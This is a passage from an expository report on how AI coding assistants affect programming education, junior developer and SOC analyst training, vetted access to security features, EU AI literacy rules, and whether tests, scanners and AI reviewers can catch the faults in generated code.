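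Harvard's introductory computer science course, CS50, has an assistant that is meant to guide students towards a solution without giving it to them. *Teaching with AI* (Elnaffar, Rashidi and Abualkishik, 2026), a review of 58 studies, cites a paper by Liu and colleagues which found that the assistant answered course questions with 88% accuracy and satisfied 73% of students. Neither figure measures whether students program better on their own afterwards. At 88% accuracy, about one answer in eight is wrong, and *Integrating AI Tutors in a Programming Course* (2024) found that tutors in another course sometimes gave potentially misleading advice.

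TUM has tested its tutor Iris more thoroughly. In a trial described in TUM's *Study Results*, 275 students on a first programming course had 90 minutes to write a program that adds up numbers in several parallel threads. The researchers randomly gave 91 of them Iris, 88 ChatGPT and 96 no AI. The published paper, "Less stress, better scores, same learning", reports that AI improved students' performance on the exercise but not their learning. ChatGPT did not leave students worse off, as it had in some other experiments, which is mildly reassuring. The result is disappointing for Iris, because holding back the solution did not help students learn more. Iris's makers ran the trial, so they had no obvious reason to play down its benefits.

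An earlier TUM study compared the same three conditions with 33 students and a harder algorithm. According to TUM (2025), the groups' performance converged, while learning scores rose slightly with Iris. With about eleven students in each group, this rise could easily be due to chance. Students using either assistant worried about becoming dependent on it, and those using ChatGPT worried more.

These results fit those of Bastani and colleagues, whose hint-only version of GPT-4 avoided the harm of giving answers but did not improve pupils' exam results. The Hechinger Report also concludes that tutors which withhold answers have not consistently beaten learning without AI. It describes a study of nearly 800 Taiwanese high-school students who learned Python with the same AI tutor. Contractor and Reyes explain that some students got practice problems whose order and difficulty adapted to them,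 while others got a fixed sequence. This design can help improve a tutor, but it can't show whether the tutor is better than none, because every student used it.

The best results for AI tutors come from other subjects. *AI tutoring outperforms in-class active learning* (2025) reports a randomised trial at Harvard in which students learned more physics, in less time, from a purpose-built AI tutor than in a class with plenty of discussion and exercises. *AI tutoring can safely and effectively support students* (2025), from Google and the mathematics platform Eedi, describes a trial with 165 pupils at five British secondary schools. Pupils helped by Google's tutoring model did at least as well as those helped by human tutors. But human tutors checked every message from the model before pupils saw it, and approved 76% with almost no changes. The trial therefore tested a supervised assistant,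 which a programming student working alone doesn't have.

#### The companies' study modes

OpenAI added a study mode to ChatGPT in July 2025, and Google and Anthropic offer similar settings. OpenAI's *Introducing study mode* describes the mode as step-by-step guidance instead of quick answers. A student who asks why her loop never ends might get a question about which line changes the loop's condition, whereas ordinary ChatGPT would probably give her the corrected loop.

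In *First Impressions of ChatGPT's Study Mode* (2025), the education writer Leon Furze points out that nothing stops a frustrated or bored student from switching from study mode back to the ordinary version. When he asked for help with a literary term, the model sent a string of questions and then a quiz without waiting for his replies. That was an early version, but better prompts can't stop students from switching. Bastani and colleagues' pupils could not switch their tutor to the version that gave answers, so we can learn little from the results about a mode that students can leave with a click.

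No independent trial seems to have measured whether a study mode improves people's unaided programming. OpenAI has developed measures of long-term learning with the University of Tartu in Estonia and a Stanford research centre, and says a randomised trial to validate them is under way. For now, the case for study modes rests on their design and on trials of other tutors.

### How assessment has changed

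Alenezi notes that models solve typical introductory programming assignments at least as well as students do. A correct take-home program therefore no longer shows what the student can do. Teachers can instead watch students work, or ask them questions about someone else's code or code they say they wrote.

The San Diego course does the first two. Its students took four exams during the term, nearly all without Copilot, and a supervised final exam. Multiple-choice and short questions about tracing, explaining, testing and debugging code counted for 70% of the final, writing code without Copilot for 15%, and a larger problem with Copilot for the other 15%. Exam work done without AI made up about half of the course grade. This grading would therefore hurt a student who could program only with Copilot much more than one who never learned to use it.

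A code-reading question might show students this program:

```python
total = 0
for n in [3, 5, 8]:
    if n > 4:
        total = total + n
```

A tracing question asks for the final value of `total`, which is 13. An explanation question asks what the program does. The San Diego teachers gave two points out of four for a correct line-by-line account and full marks only for stating the program's purpose, which here is to add up the numbers greater than four. The distinction matters for checking an assistant's work, because a reviewer who can follow each line but can't say what the lines do together can't compare the program with the request. Explaining a correct program is still different from noticing a faulty one, so an exam meant to test reviewing also needs programs with bugs.

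Grades on the course's projects, where students could use Copilot freely, show why such exams are useful. On the exams, Black, Latino, Native American and Pacific Islander students scored 8.4 points lower than others after adjusting for factors such as income, and students with earlier programming experience scored about 3 points higher. Neither gap appeared in the project grades. Vadaparty and colleagues write that projects reduce inequality, though they suspect that nearly everyone scored too high for differences to show. The projects may well have let more students succeed at something ambitious, but equal grades for work done with Copilot don't mean equal knowledge, as Balepur and colleagues' experiment with an agent showed.

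The third approach is to have students explain their submitted code aloud. A teacher might point to a condition and ask what would happen if the list were empty. Bergh and Vassar provide indirect evidence that such questions can reveal who did the work. Two days after writing their programs, 41% of the students who had used ChatGPT could not recall a single line, compared with 4% of those who had worked without AI. Using recall to detect AI use would still miss more than half of the users and wrongly flag a few students who had worked without it. Questions about why the code works are fairer because they test understanding, regardless of how the student gained it. A student who let an assistant write the program and then studied it until she could answer has learned some of what the assignment was meant to teach.

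### Which methods improved unaided work

Helping students finish a task is much easier than improving what they can do afterwards. In *Studying the effect of AI Code Generators on Supporting Novice Learners* (2023), the experiment by Kazemitabaar and colleagues described earlier, novices with a code generator were also more eager to continue programming than those without one. That eagerness could matter a great deal because many students give up programming, but the novices with the generator did not retain measurably more.

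Showing students how code runs may do more, though the evidence is mixed. *AI-Generated Traces for Novice Programmers* (2026) tested AI-generated traces, which show step by step how a program runs. At Delft University of Technology, students with the traces did better immediately afterwards, mainly on while-loops, which repeat as long as a condition is true. At the University of Toronto, the traces had no overall effect.

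The table separates results with help from results without it:

| Method | Compared with | With the method in use | Without AI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Explaining AI code before using it | free use of AI | equally good websites, built more slowly | many more people repaired the bug |
| Iris | no AI | better performance | no better learning |
| Code generator for novices | no AI | better coding, more eagerness | no significant difference |
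| Copilot from the first week | international averages | larger projects | similar at reading code |
| Planted bugs | ordinary faults | more editing, more successful repairs | not tested |
| CS50's assistant | nothing | 73% of students satisfied | no result in the review |

Only the explanation requirement produced a clear gain in unaided work over free use of AI. People who had built their websites without any AI repaired the bug slightly more often than those who had to explain their code, but in 90 minutes they had met only 42% of the project's requirements, and the paper confirms a working enrolment feature only for the two groups with AI. If the result holds up, students who must explain generated code can build more in the same time than they could without AI and still understand enough of it to fix it. There is no evidence yet that any of these methods teaches unaided skill better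 than having students write the code themselves.

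## Training and supervision at work and in security jobs

A graduate who can write and explain a program still has a lot to learn before she can review one at work. No course teaches a firm's own rules, such as how its accountants handle corrected invoices. New programmers and security analysts have usually learned such things on the job, by doing small tasks that someone more experienced checked.

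### How juniors learned the job

Suppose a new programmer's first task is to correct the format of a date on customers' invoices. The change takes one line, but to find that line she has to follow an invoice from the database to the web page. She changes the database query, and the reviewer rejects this because the tax report uses the same query and needs the old format. She now knows how two parts of the system depend on each other, and her mistake has done the firm very little harm.

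*From Correctness to Collaboration* (2025) describes interviews with 15 developers, most of whom had more than six years' experience and had supervised or mentored juniors several times. The developers expected juniors to learn what good code is through mentoring and repeated code review, and to pick up the team's unwritten standards as well as its documented ones. They did not expect beginners to see the importance of quality straight away, because they regarded quality as a way of communicating with engineers who would read the code later. The interviews do not show how much juniors learn.

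In *Agents That Teach*, Mehra, Suri and colleagues (2026) use the term "incidental learning" for knowledge that people gain as a by-product of solving problems. Before AI, a developer who hit an error would search for answers, read explanations, compare possible fixes and write one she could justify. Now she can paste the error into an agent and get a working fix in seconds. An agent given the invoice task might read the tax report's code and leave the query alone, so the new programmer would never learn about the tax report.

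Junior SOC analysts learned in a similar way from first-level alerts, closing the harmless ones and passing the rest to someone senior. This repetitive work shows them what normal traffic looks like. After closing fifty alerts about the nightly backup, an analyst knows its usual time and destination, and notices when a transfer of the same size goes somewhere else. If an assistant closes those fifty alerts, the suspicious transfer may be the first large one she has examined. The university SOC gave the Companion only to experienced analysts, so its newcomers investigated alerts by hand.

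An assistant can also help juniors learn, for instance by answering questions they would be embarrassed to ask a colleague or by letting them take on larger tasks sooner. But they may not use it that way without supervision. In Balepur and colleagues' web game experiment, people who pasted in prompts and accepted edits automatically had lower comprehension, though weaker programmers may be more likely to work that way. Participants also preferred the agent because it was quick and easy, even though they reported understanding their code less well.

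### Senior review and pairing

*AI-coding tools could be breaking the junior engineer pipeline* (Stokel-Walker, 2026) reports that Adrian Harwood, who leads research software engineering at the University of Manchester, thinks it is futile to stop juniors from using AI. His department takes undergraduates on year-long placements, and nobody junior does a project alone. Senior engineers review the juniors' proposed changes, including AI-written ones, and point out problems that the juniors may not have the experience to see. They also teach juniors "how to police the tool" by reviewing its output and understanding why some of its choices could cause trouble. Harwood gives no figures on whether the department's juniors learn more as a result.

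Senior review can protect the software even if the junior engineer learns nothing, as long as the reviewer catches the faults. The reviewer's response affects whether the junior also learns. Suppose she submits an AI-written invoice page without an authorization check. The reviewer can make the page safe by adding the missing line himself, but she will probably make the same mistake again. If he instead asks her which line stops one customer from opening another's invoice, she has to look for the check and find out for herself that it is missing.

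Asking a junior about a fault takes a reviewer longer than fixing it, and juniors who use agents submit more changes to ask about. Suppose a junior used to submit four changes a week and now submits ten. At half an hour each, the weekly review time rises from two hours to five, or 15 hours for a senior engineer with three juniors. The engineer will be tempted to fix the faults without asking about them or to approve the changes after a quick look.

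Pairing, where two people work on a task together, takes even more of a senior engineer's time. But it lets the senior engineer see how the junior reaches a decision, which a finished change doesn't show. If they use an agent, the junior can say what she expects the change to contain before either of them reads it, and the senior engineer can see what she left out.

An employer could put such arrangements in writing, for example by requiring juniors to explain every AI-written change before anyone reviews it and allowing only senior engineers to approve changes to login or payment code. Manchester's practice of never giving a junior a solo project is easier to enforce, because the manager who assigns the projects can ensure it is followed. A reviewer who has to judge whether an explanation is good enough may accept a weak one when a deadline is close.

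### Coding agents that teach

In July 2026, Mehra and colleagues at the consultancy Accenture proposed using coding tools for some of the teaching. Their system, SHIELD, runs beside a coding agent and looks for things in the agent's work that the developer may not understand.

Their example is a payment system that sends an automatic message when something happens, such as a customer paying, and tries again if the message doesn't get through. The retries come at fixed intervals, and the developer asks the agent to fix them. The agent makes each wait longer than the last, for instance one second, then two, then four, and adds a small random delay. This spreads out the retries, because thousands of messages can fail together when the receiving server breaks down, and resending them all at the same moment could overload it again.

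SHIELD has the coding agent record what it changed, why, which alternatives it considered and how confident it was. Another agent identifies the concepts involved and compares them with a map of what the developer seems to know, initially based on code she wrote herself. If a concept seems new to her, such as growing and random delays, a question about it appears in a queue in her editor, and she can answer in her own words whenever she likes. If her answer reveals a gap, she gets a short lesson and later another question to check whether she has understood. SHIELD then updates the map, which helps it choose the next question.

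Mehra and colleagues built a prototype that works with Claude Code and uses OpenAI's GPT-5.1 to write questions and grade the answers. They showed it to people inside Accenture and report promising feedback, but when the paper appeared, nobody had tested whether it teaches developers anything. They plan user studies.

The experiment in which people had to explain AI code before using it gives SHIELD only limited support, because the experiment's tool withheld the code until the explanation was good enough. Mehra and colleagues deliberately designed SHIELD not to block developers, to avoid interrupting their work. A junior developer with a deadline can therefore leave SHIELD's questions unanswered for weeks, and those who understand least may be the most likely to do so.

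SHIELD also depends on the coding agent's explanation of its own reasons. If the agent overlooked that the payment provider already resends failed messages, the lesson could teach the developer the same mistake. A lesson can explain why the retry delays are random, but the developer would also need practice tracing faults to find one in a retry system.

### What security training sets as a baseline

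The NICE framework, which the US standards agency NIST maintains, lists the tasks, knowledge and skills involved in cybersecurity jobs. In June 2025 NIST announced that it would add an area called AI Security (Livesay, 2025, *NIST plans to integrate artificial intelligence skills, roles*). NIST describes the area as a broad, basic set of knowledge and skill statements.

The US cybersecurity agency CISA publishes a definition of the area that covers protecting AI systems from attack, keeping them contained where people use them, and countering AI that is malicious or has malicious users. Checking an assistant's work is a different skill. An analyst could be good at everything in the definition and still not notice that a summary of a mailbox break-in leaves out the attacker's forwarding rule.

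A NIST poster (2024) had already separated the security of AI systems, which the new area would cover, from the use of AI in security work. To cover that use, NIST expected to revise the descriptions of individual jobs or write new ones. This makes sense for verification, because an analyst who checks an assistant's summary of an incident mainly needs to know how to investigate incidents, and a general list of AI skills can't replace that knowledge.

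SANS, a security training company, matches its courses and GIAC certificates to the jobs in the framework. This helps an employer find a course that covers the right subjects, but it is not evidence that people who finish the course catch more of an assistant's mistakes. The words "AI security" can mislead an employer here too. According to its course page, SANS's *SEC536* teaches people to attack AI systems, not to judge an assistant's answers.

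A course for that purpose could have learners investigate alerts by hand from raw logs before they see an assistant's summaries. It could then mix correct summaries with faulty ones, much like the planted bugs in the Auckland programming course, and test learners on alerts with known answers before and after the course. If half of the learners started with the assistant instead, the tests would also show whether the order matters.

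### Access to the strongest security features

Anthropic and OpenAI make their models refuse some security requests, such as writing code that exploits a flaw, and relax these limits for vetted applicants. Anthropic's Cyber Verification Program has three levels of access. Defense Access is for work such as analysing malware and confirming vulnerabilities. Red Team Access is for organisations that test defences by attacking them with permission, and Specialized Access is for those that test critical systems such as power grids. OpenAI has two levels, Daybreak Blue and Daybreak Red, and only organisations can apply for Red.

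The conditions mostly concern who the applicants are, what they want to do and how well they protect their accounts:

| Applicant | Identity, purpose and security | Evidence of competence |
|---|---|---|
| Individual, Anthropic Defense Access | photo ID, description of the work | none listed |
| In-house team, Anthropic Red Team Access | proof of a security programme, background checks, permission for each test | certificates, published work or a test report |
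| Established testing firm, Anthropic Red Team Access | business verification, background checks | a professional listing or membership, an accreditation, or credit for finding a flaw |
| Smaller testing firm, Anthropic Red Team Access | a year of registration, public information about its services, background checks | at least two testers with certificates, and evidence of recent work |
| Individual, OpenAI Daybreak Blue | age 18 or over, identity check, paid plan, hardware security key | none listed |
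| Organisation, OpenAI Daybreak | identification and intended use | possible questions about "cybersecurity capabilities" |

Certificates are mandatory only for the smaller testing firms. One that Anthropic accepts is the OSCP, which requires candidates to break into practice computers in a day-long exam. This tests skill, but only two people at the firm need such a certificate, while Red Team Access can cover up to 75. OpenAI's question about capabilities could also concern skill, but the company names no exam or minimum standard.

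The programmes are meant to prevent misuse. OpenAI's *Request Daybreak Access* explains that asking for identification and a professional purpose reduces the risk of misuse. A competence test would be a poor way to prevent it, because a skilled criminal could pass and an honest beginner would fail. The certificates Anthropic asks for mainly help show that a firm really does security testing.

The conditions therefore do little about overreliance. An honest bug hunter with a passport and a paid plan can apply for Defense Access, accept a false finding he cannot check, and send it to a project like curl. People who review code or sort alerts don't need to apply, because Anthropic's ordinary models are open for that work. Requiring an exam would keep out some people who cannot check a finding, but it could also shut out a small hospital's only technician, who has nobody else to ask. OpenAI took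 another approach to such organisations in September 2026, when it committed $1 billion through *Daybreak for Frontline Defenders* to subsidised access, training and technical support for people who protect essential services.

### The EU's duty to support AI literacy

European employers have a legal duty to teach staff about AI, including those outside security. According to a guide by SAIG, Article 4 of the EU's AI Act has applied since 2 February 2025 to every organisation that provides or uses AI, whatever the system's risk. The original text, the European Union's *Article 4 AI literacy* (2024), required organisations to take measures to ensure "to their best extent, a sufficient level of AI literacy" among employees and anyone else who operated AI on their behalf, such as contractors.

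The European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026), known as the Digital Omnibus on AI, weakened this duty. It entered into force on 27 July 2026, as White & Case's *EU AI Omnibus enters into force, amending the AI Act* notes. Organisations must now take measures to support the development of AI literacy, but they do not have to guarantee that any individual reaches a specific level. According to the regulation's preamble, a strict duty does not suit every kind of organisation and particularly burdens smaller firms. The European Commission had wanted to drop the direct duty on organisations altogether, but Cuatrecasas' *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published* (2026) reports that the European Parliament kept it in this milder form.

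Suppose a software firm gives its staff a one-hour course, and a third of them still believe that code is secure if it passes the agent's tests. Under the old wording, a regulator could have asked whether the firm had done its best to bring its staff to a sufficient level. Under the new wording, the firm can more easily defend itself by pointing to the course, though it must still consider what its staff know and how they use the system.

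Germany's regulator, the Bundesnetzagentur, says in *AI literacy* that the EU AI Act requires no standard course, certificate or AI officer. It warns that a lack of AI literacy can count as a breach of an organisation's duty of care, especially if somebody is harmed. It recommends that organisations record what they have done.

The Act defines AI literacy as the skills, knowledge and understanding that people need to use AI in an informed way and to be aware of its opportunities, risks and possible harms. Baseline knowledge is knowledge of the field in which they use it. After a good course in AI literacy, a ward clerk may know that coding agents make mistakes and that patient data needs protection. She still can't see that the login page the agent wrote lets one patient open another's file. A programmer might see this at once but not know that the assistant's provider may keep any code pasted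 into it.

General awareness may do little on its own, since Virk and Liu's participants missed serious flaws despite repeated warnings. A literacy course could help more by teaching people when to ask someone else, which is part of baseline knowledge. The Bundesnetzagentur also suggests role-specific training after the basics. Firms could use this to teach programmers about authorization, though the Act doesn't require them to.

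### Regular practice without AI

In 2013 the US Federal Aviation Administration recommended a more direct remedy for lost practice when it advised airlines to give pilots opportunities to fly by hand, for example when their workload is low. This resembles Bainbridge's proposal for plant operators. Mehra and colleagues mention minimum amounts of unaided practice and simulator training among the remedies proposed for aviation and medicine.

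Flying by hand costs an airline little, because the plane arrives at about the same time. A developer who works without an assistant may produce less. If AI raises her output by a proportion g, and she works without it for a share s of her time, the share of output that her employer loses is:

s × g / (1 + g)

Suppose a developer produces 30% more with AI (g = 0.3) and spends half a day a week without it (s = 0.1). Her employer loses about 2.3% of her output, or roughly half a developer's work across a team of twenty who all do the same. If AI doubles her output, the loss is 5%. Even if AI raised her output a hundredfold, the loss would not exceed 10%, the share of her time she spends without it. If AI doubles a junior's output and she works without it two days a week, the loss is 20%.

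The choice of task matters as much as the number of hours. If programmers resemble the pilots in the simulator study, a developer should spend the half day tracing a fault through unfamiliar code instead of writing short functions. Nobody knows yet whether half a day a week is enough.

Analysts can't safely slow down in the middle of an attack, so a SOC could have them practise on closed incidents. Two hours of practice a week would take up 5% of each analyst's time, or 24 hours a week for a team of twelve. If an alert takes 20 minutes with an assistant, the team would leave 72 alerts unopened every week, a serious problem for a SOC that already has a backlog.

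Analysts could instead practise on current alerts that are not urgent, writing down their own verdict before they open the assistant's. If an investigation takes 30 minutes by hand and 10 with the assistant, five such alerts a week would take each analyst an extra 100 minutes, or about 4% of a 40-hour week. The SOC still gets those alerts closed, and it also gets verdicts that the assistant has not influenced. Those verdicts would help it find out whether the assistant is dismissing real attacks, which the trial of the Companion could not show.

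## Whether tests, scanners and AI reviewers can replace the user's knowledge

Regular practice without AI makes sense only if people will still need to check the AI's work. Software firms already use tests and scanners to catch faults that reviewers miss, and many now have a second AI model review the first one's code. If these checks work well enough, the user may not need to know much about code.

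### The case for leaving it to machines

The programmers who judged generated assertions caught only half of the faulty ones, so an automated reviewer could perform poorly and still do better than they did. Machines also find flaws in real software that people have overlooked. Anthropic reported that Mythos Preview found more than ten thousand serious vulnerabilities in a few weeks in 2026.

At least one company has moved much of its code review to AI without obvious harm. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) examines a mid-sized software firm whose technology chief asked engineers in June 2025 to double their output of merged changes within a year. By April 2026, the share of changes reviewed by a human had fallen from 89% to 68%, while the share reviewed by an AI had risen from about 19% to 84%. The share of changes that undid earlier ones fell slightly.

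This is good evidence that machines can do much of the checking, but it doesn't show that people can do without knowledge of their own. Anthropic's figure leaves out whatever the model missed, and the organisations in its programme maintain critical systems, so they presumably had people who could judge a report. Engineers undo a change only after someone notices a problem. As He and colleagues acknowledge, their measures miss undiscovered defects and code that is becoming hard to maintain.

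Newer models do not always write safer code. In *Securing AI-Generated Code*, Surikov (2026) had four Claude models write short Python programs and counted the warnings from two security scanners. First drafts by Sonnet 5 averaged 1.44 warnings, more than the 1.09 for the older Sonnet 4.6. Opus 4.8 had the lowest average, 0.82. *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?* (2026) describes an earlier study of three generations of models up to March 2025, in which the last generation produced working code for every task but did not consistently produce fewer vulnerabilities.

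### Tests that repeat the code's mistake

A test gives a program an input and compares the result with an expected answer. How much it catches depends on where that answer came from. Suppose an accountant asks an assistant to charge a 2% fee on invoices that are more than 30 days overdue, and to test its work. It returns this:

```python
def late_fee(amount, issued, due, today):
    if (today - issued).days > 30:
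        return amount * 0.02
    return 0

def test_late_fee():
    issued, due = date(2026, 3, 1), date(2026, 3, 31)
    assert late_fee(500, issued, due, date(2026, 4, 10)) == 10
    assert late_fee(500, issued, due, date(2026, 3, 20)) == 0
```

The function counts from the day the firm issued the invoice instead of the day payment was due. On 10 April this invoice is only ten days overdue, so the customer owes no fee. The first assertion checks for a fee of $10 because it repeats the same mistake. Both assertions pass, and together they run every line of the function.

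The request was right and the code departs from it, so this is an error against the specification. Tools can find such errors if the expected answers come from the request rather than the code. The accountant can also find it without reading Python, by calculating the fee for one invoice by hand.

Suppose the assistant fixes the function, but the accountant forgot to mention that the firm replaces a wrong invoice with a second one under the same number. The function then charges a late fee on the replaced invoice. The code does exactly what the accountant requested, so every test based on the request will pass, however capable the model that writes it. The error is in the specification itself, and to catch it, someone has to know the firm's custom and realise that it matters here.

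Models also write misleading tests of this kind for real code. *Evaluating and Mitigating the Misguidance Effect of Buggy Code* (Zhao, Zhou and Cohen, 2026) describes a Java function that should treat two pieces of text as equal if they contain the same characters, even if they are stored differently. Given a faulty version that treated them as unequal, a model wrote a test requiring that wrong answer. The researchers then had a model describe what the function was meant to do, and gave only that description to the model writing the test. The new test exposed the fault.

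Konstantinou, Tambon and Papadakis (2026), in *On the risk of coding before testing*, measured the effect with five models, including GPT-5-mini and Claude Haiku 4.5. When a model wrote tests after producing faulty code, the tests caught about 14% of the faults. When it started afresh from the task description, they caught about 25%. Both sets of tests ran at least 95% of the code's lines on average, so line coverage, the usual measure of thorough testing, would not have revealed how many faults they missed. The researchers deliberately kept faults that were hard to expose, and the models were fairly small, so everyday results may be better. Still, someone who asks an assistant for code and then for tests should know that passing every test is weak evidence that the code is correct, and should supply a few expected answers of their own.

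### Scanners and the checks that disappear

A static scanner reads code without running it and looks for known dangerous patterns, such as a database command built from text that a visitor typed. It can search a large program in minutes. But it compares the code with general rules, not with what this program should allow, so it can easily overlook a missing authorization check like the one on the invoice page.

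Scanners can also miss a model's removal of existing protection. *SCAFFOLD-CEGIS* (Chen, Bian and colleagues, 2026) describes a case in which a model asked to simplify some code deleted the function that checked users' input. Two scanners reported no new problem because the remaining code matched none of their patterns. In another case, a model asked for an administrator shortcut created a way around the permission check.

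Chen and colleagues also tried blocking every revision that caused a new scanner warning. A second model then judged that hidden security problems had increased in 20.8% of the programs, compared with 12.5% when no scanner was used. The total number of changed lines was almost the same in both conditions, which doesn't support their suggestion that passing the scan encouraged the model to make bigger changes. The percentages correspond to about 20 and 12 cases out of 96, so chance could explain the difference. The result is better evidence that scanners miss these problems than that they cause them.

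A scanner's user has to know which dangers the scanner looks for and which of its warnings are false alarms. If a program handles other people's data, a clean report doesn't mean anyone has checked who is allowed to see that data.

### Security instructions for 400 web applications

Most people never mention security in their prompts, so a standard paragraph they can paste in might make up for some of the knowledge they lack. Andročec (2026), in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, tested this on complete web applications. He wrote 100 descriptions, ranging from a page that greets a visitor by name to platforms with several kinds of user. Claude Code (running Opus 4.8) and OpenAI's Codex (running GPT-5.5) each built every application twice, first from a prompt with only the description and a request for a runnable application, and then from the same prompt plus a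 fixed paragraph requiring protections such as safe database queries, strong password storage and access control.

The outcome was the number of problems that a fixed set of scanners reported, after removing likely false alarms:

| Measure | Plain prompt | With security paragraph |
|---|---|---|
| Findings per application, Claude Code | 20.2 | 13.2 |
| Findings per application, Codex | 20.0 | 13.8 |
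| Outside packages per application, Claude Code | 3.2 | 6.3 |
| Outside packages per application, Codex | 3.0 | 6.5 |
| Serious findings in the applications' own code, total | 103 | 54 |
| Serious warnings about outside packages, total | 198 | 344 |

The paragraph reduced findings by about 35% (95% confidence interval 29% to 40%), with similar reductions for both tools. It also roughly doubled the number of packages (ready-made code written by other people) that the applications relied on. Serious warnings about packages rose with that number, but the rate per package did not. The benefit seemed smaller in complicated applications (around 26% to 30%) than in simple ones (about 40%), though this difference is uncertain.

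#### What a count of findings leaves out

The findings are scanner reports, and nobody confirmed that an attacker could exploit any of them. The count gives a missing browser setting the same weight as a flaw that lets an attacker steal the whole database. Just over half of the findings, and most of the improvement, came from a scan that mostly detects missing browser settings. The instructions in the paragraph named several of these settings, so the experiment partly measured whether the tools followed instructions.

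The paragraph also required the tools to let users act only on their own records. A general scanner has no information about which customer owns which invoice, so the number of findings is weak evidence of whether the tools met this requirement. An application could have seven fewer findings and still show customers each other's invoices.

A low count can also mean that the scanners checked less. PHP applications averaged 0.6 findings from static scanning, compared with about 7 for the other languages. Scans of the running applications, which worked the same way for every language, found almost equal numbers of problems, so PHP was not safer. Its static count was low because no tool checked PHP packages for known flaws, and the only scanner made specifically for PHP found four problems in 60 applications.

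Andročec notes that the paragraph changed both the security instructions and the size of the application, so the experiment can't separate their effects. Each tool also built each version only once. The result still supports the objection, because a person who knows nothing about security can paste in a paragraph and probably get a better-configured application. Such a paragraph may not help much with existing software. Andročec cites a test of 186 feature requests in real projects, in which only 11.8% of the best agent's solutions were secure and hints about the vulnerability did not solve the problem.

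### A second model as reviewer

An AI reviewer can consider what code is for, which a pattern-matching scanner can't. In Surikov's system, one model writes a program, another lists its security weaknesses, and the first repairs them using background information on each weakness. This reduced scanner warnings by 42% on average across the four Claude models. Adding the scanners' warnings to the repair instructions raised the reduction to 57%. The same scanners then graded the result, so some of the extra reduction may come from tailoring the repairs to what those scanners detect.

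Opus 4.8, whose first drafts were the cleanest, improved by only 9% with the reviewer alone. Depending on the model and method, 15% to 22% of repairs introduced at least one new kind of warning. The system therefore helped on average but could not guarantee that any particular program became safer.

An AI reviewer that has only the code and the request also lacks the facts that nobody wrote down. It might well flag the choice to run the late fee from the issue date, but it can't account for the fact that a corrected invoice replaces the first one unless somebody supplies it. Two models that agree may have made the same assumption. The user has to supply the missing facts and decide what to do when the two models disagree.

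### What repeated revision does to secure code

Shukla, Joshi and Syed (2025) found in *Security Degradation in Iterative AI Code Generation* that code became less secure when OpenAI's GPT-4o revised it repeatedly. They started with ten C and Java programs that experts and scanners had judged free of vulnerabilities. The model revised each program ten times in a row, with no human involved between rounds. In four separate versions of the experiment, they asked it for faster code, more features, better security or general improvement.

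Programs averaged 2.1 vulnerabilities in the early revisions, 4.7 in the middle ones and 6.2 in the last three. In one case, a request for speed led the model to remove a data size check in the first round, and by the tenth the program handled memory in risky ways. Requests for features produced 158 vulnerabilities in total, and requests for security produced 38. The often-quoted 37.6% increase in critical vulnerabilities after five rounds appears in the paper's abstract, but the results section doesn't show the calculation behind it.

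Newer models still show some of this degradation, though apparently less. In Chen and colleagues' experiments, 43.7% of GPT-4o's programs had more vulnerabilities after ten rounds than at the start. The figures were 10.5% for GPT-5-nano, 6.2% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 4.2% for DeepSeek-V3. The GPT-4o figure counts vulnerabilities of every severity, while the others count only the two most serious levels, so part of the drop may come from the narrower count. Some of the paper's detailed percentages are also impossible with the 16 programs per category it describes, so even the newer figures are rough. None of these models is among the strongest available in late 2026. *Beyond Passing Tests* (2026), a review of methods for improving generated code, also cautions that studies of this kind use few models and few starting programs.

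Feedback from a scanner can help a model fix security problems, but the repairs can also create new ones. *Does Fixing Break Security?* (Agyekum and Santos, 2026) tested two older models on files that set up cloud servers and storage. The models repaired the files up to five times using a scanner's error messages, and the share of security checks that the files passed rose from 73% to 82.6%. In 13.8% of cases, a repair broke at least one check that had passed before. The researchers prefer a stricter figure of 3.3%, which counts a check only if it goes from passing everywhere to failing everywhere. That figure leaves out real losses, such as a repair that removes encryption from one of two storage areas, so the true rate is probably between 3.3% and 13.8%.

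These results suggest that it is better to give the model a specific fault to fix than to run unsupervised rounds of "make it better". The user has to know which protections the revision must keep, or have a test for each one.

### Safe defaults in the platform

A platform can also prevent some mistakes regardless of what its user knows. It can keep visitors' text separate from database commands, or give every form the secret value that stops request forgery, without anyone having to remember to ask for these protections.

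Andročec's experiment suggests how much default packages could matter. He examined 79 applications for which the agent read the security paragraph and then picked packages for tasks such as storing passwords. In 12 of them, it picked only packages that need no extra tools during installation, and these applications had no serious package warnings. The other 67 averaged 5.1 each. A platform that offered only the safer packages might avoid most of those warnings, but this is still a hypothesis because the agents chose the packages themselves and 12 applications is a small sample.

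Defaults work best for rules that nearly every application shares. A platform could also let customers see only their own records by default, which would protect the invoice page, but somebody would have to decide who gets an exception, such as an accountant who needs everyone's invoices. An assistant can also switch a default off, for instance by accepting every server certificate to get rid of an error. The user doesn't need to understand encryption to be safe here, but does need to know that turning off a security check doesn't fix the underlying problem.

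### Nobody has time to read

Knowledge doesn't help if a reviewer has no time to use it. At the company that He and colleagues studied, the number of proposed changes grew to 3.1 times its level in early 2025, but the number of reviewers grew only 1.5 times. The share of changes with a human reviewer's comment fell from about 39% to 21%. Humans still approved about half of all changes without commenting.

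For every 100 changes in the earlier period, there were 310 in the later one. Given these shares, the number of changes with a written human comment rose from about 39 to 65, while the number that no human reviewed rose from about 11 to 99.

Other projects have kept more human review. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examined open-source AI projects and found that people reviewed about 80% of the changes that showed no signs of AI use. The typical review rate for AI-written changes was 8.1 percentage points lower, but this gap disappeared when the analysis weighted the changes by contributor.

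*Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026) reports interviews with 24 developers who had heavy review loads. Some used AI to explain changes or to pick out the ones that deserved attention. This can let an expert spend an hour on the login code instead of on twenty wording changes. But a change that the AI wrongly ranks as routine may never reach anyone who would recognise the danger.

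### Three positions on the baseline

Shukla and colleagues hold that human expertise remains essential. They want a developer to review the code between revisions, with at most three rounds allowed before a review. Their experiment shows why some outside check is needed, but it included no human review, so it can't show that developers would have caught the vulnerabilities. Programmers often accept faulty code, so a rule that requires review may achieve little if it doesn't also require a reviewer who can find the faults.

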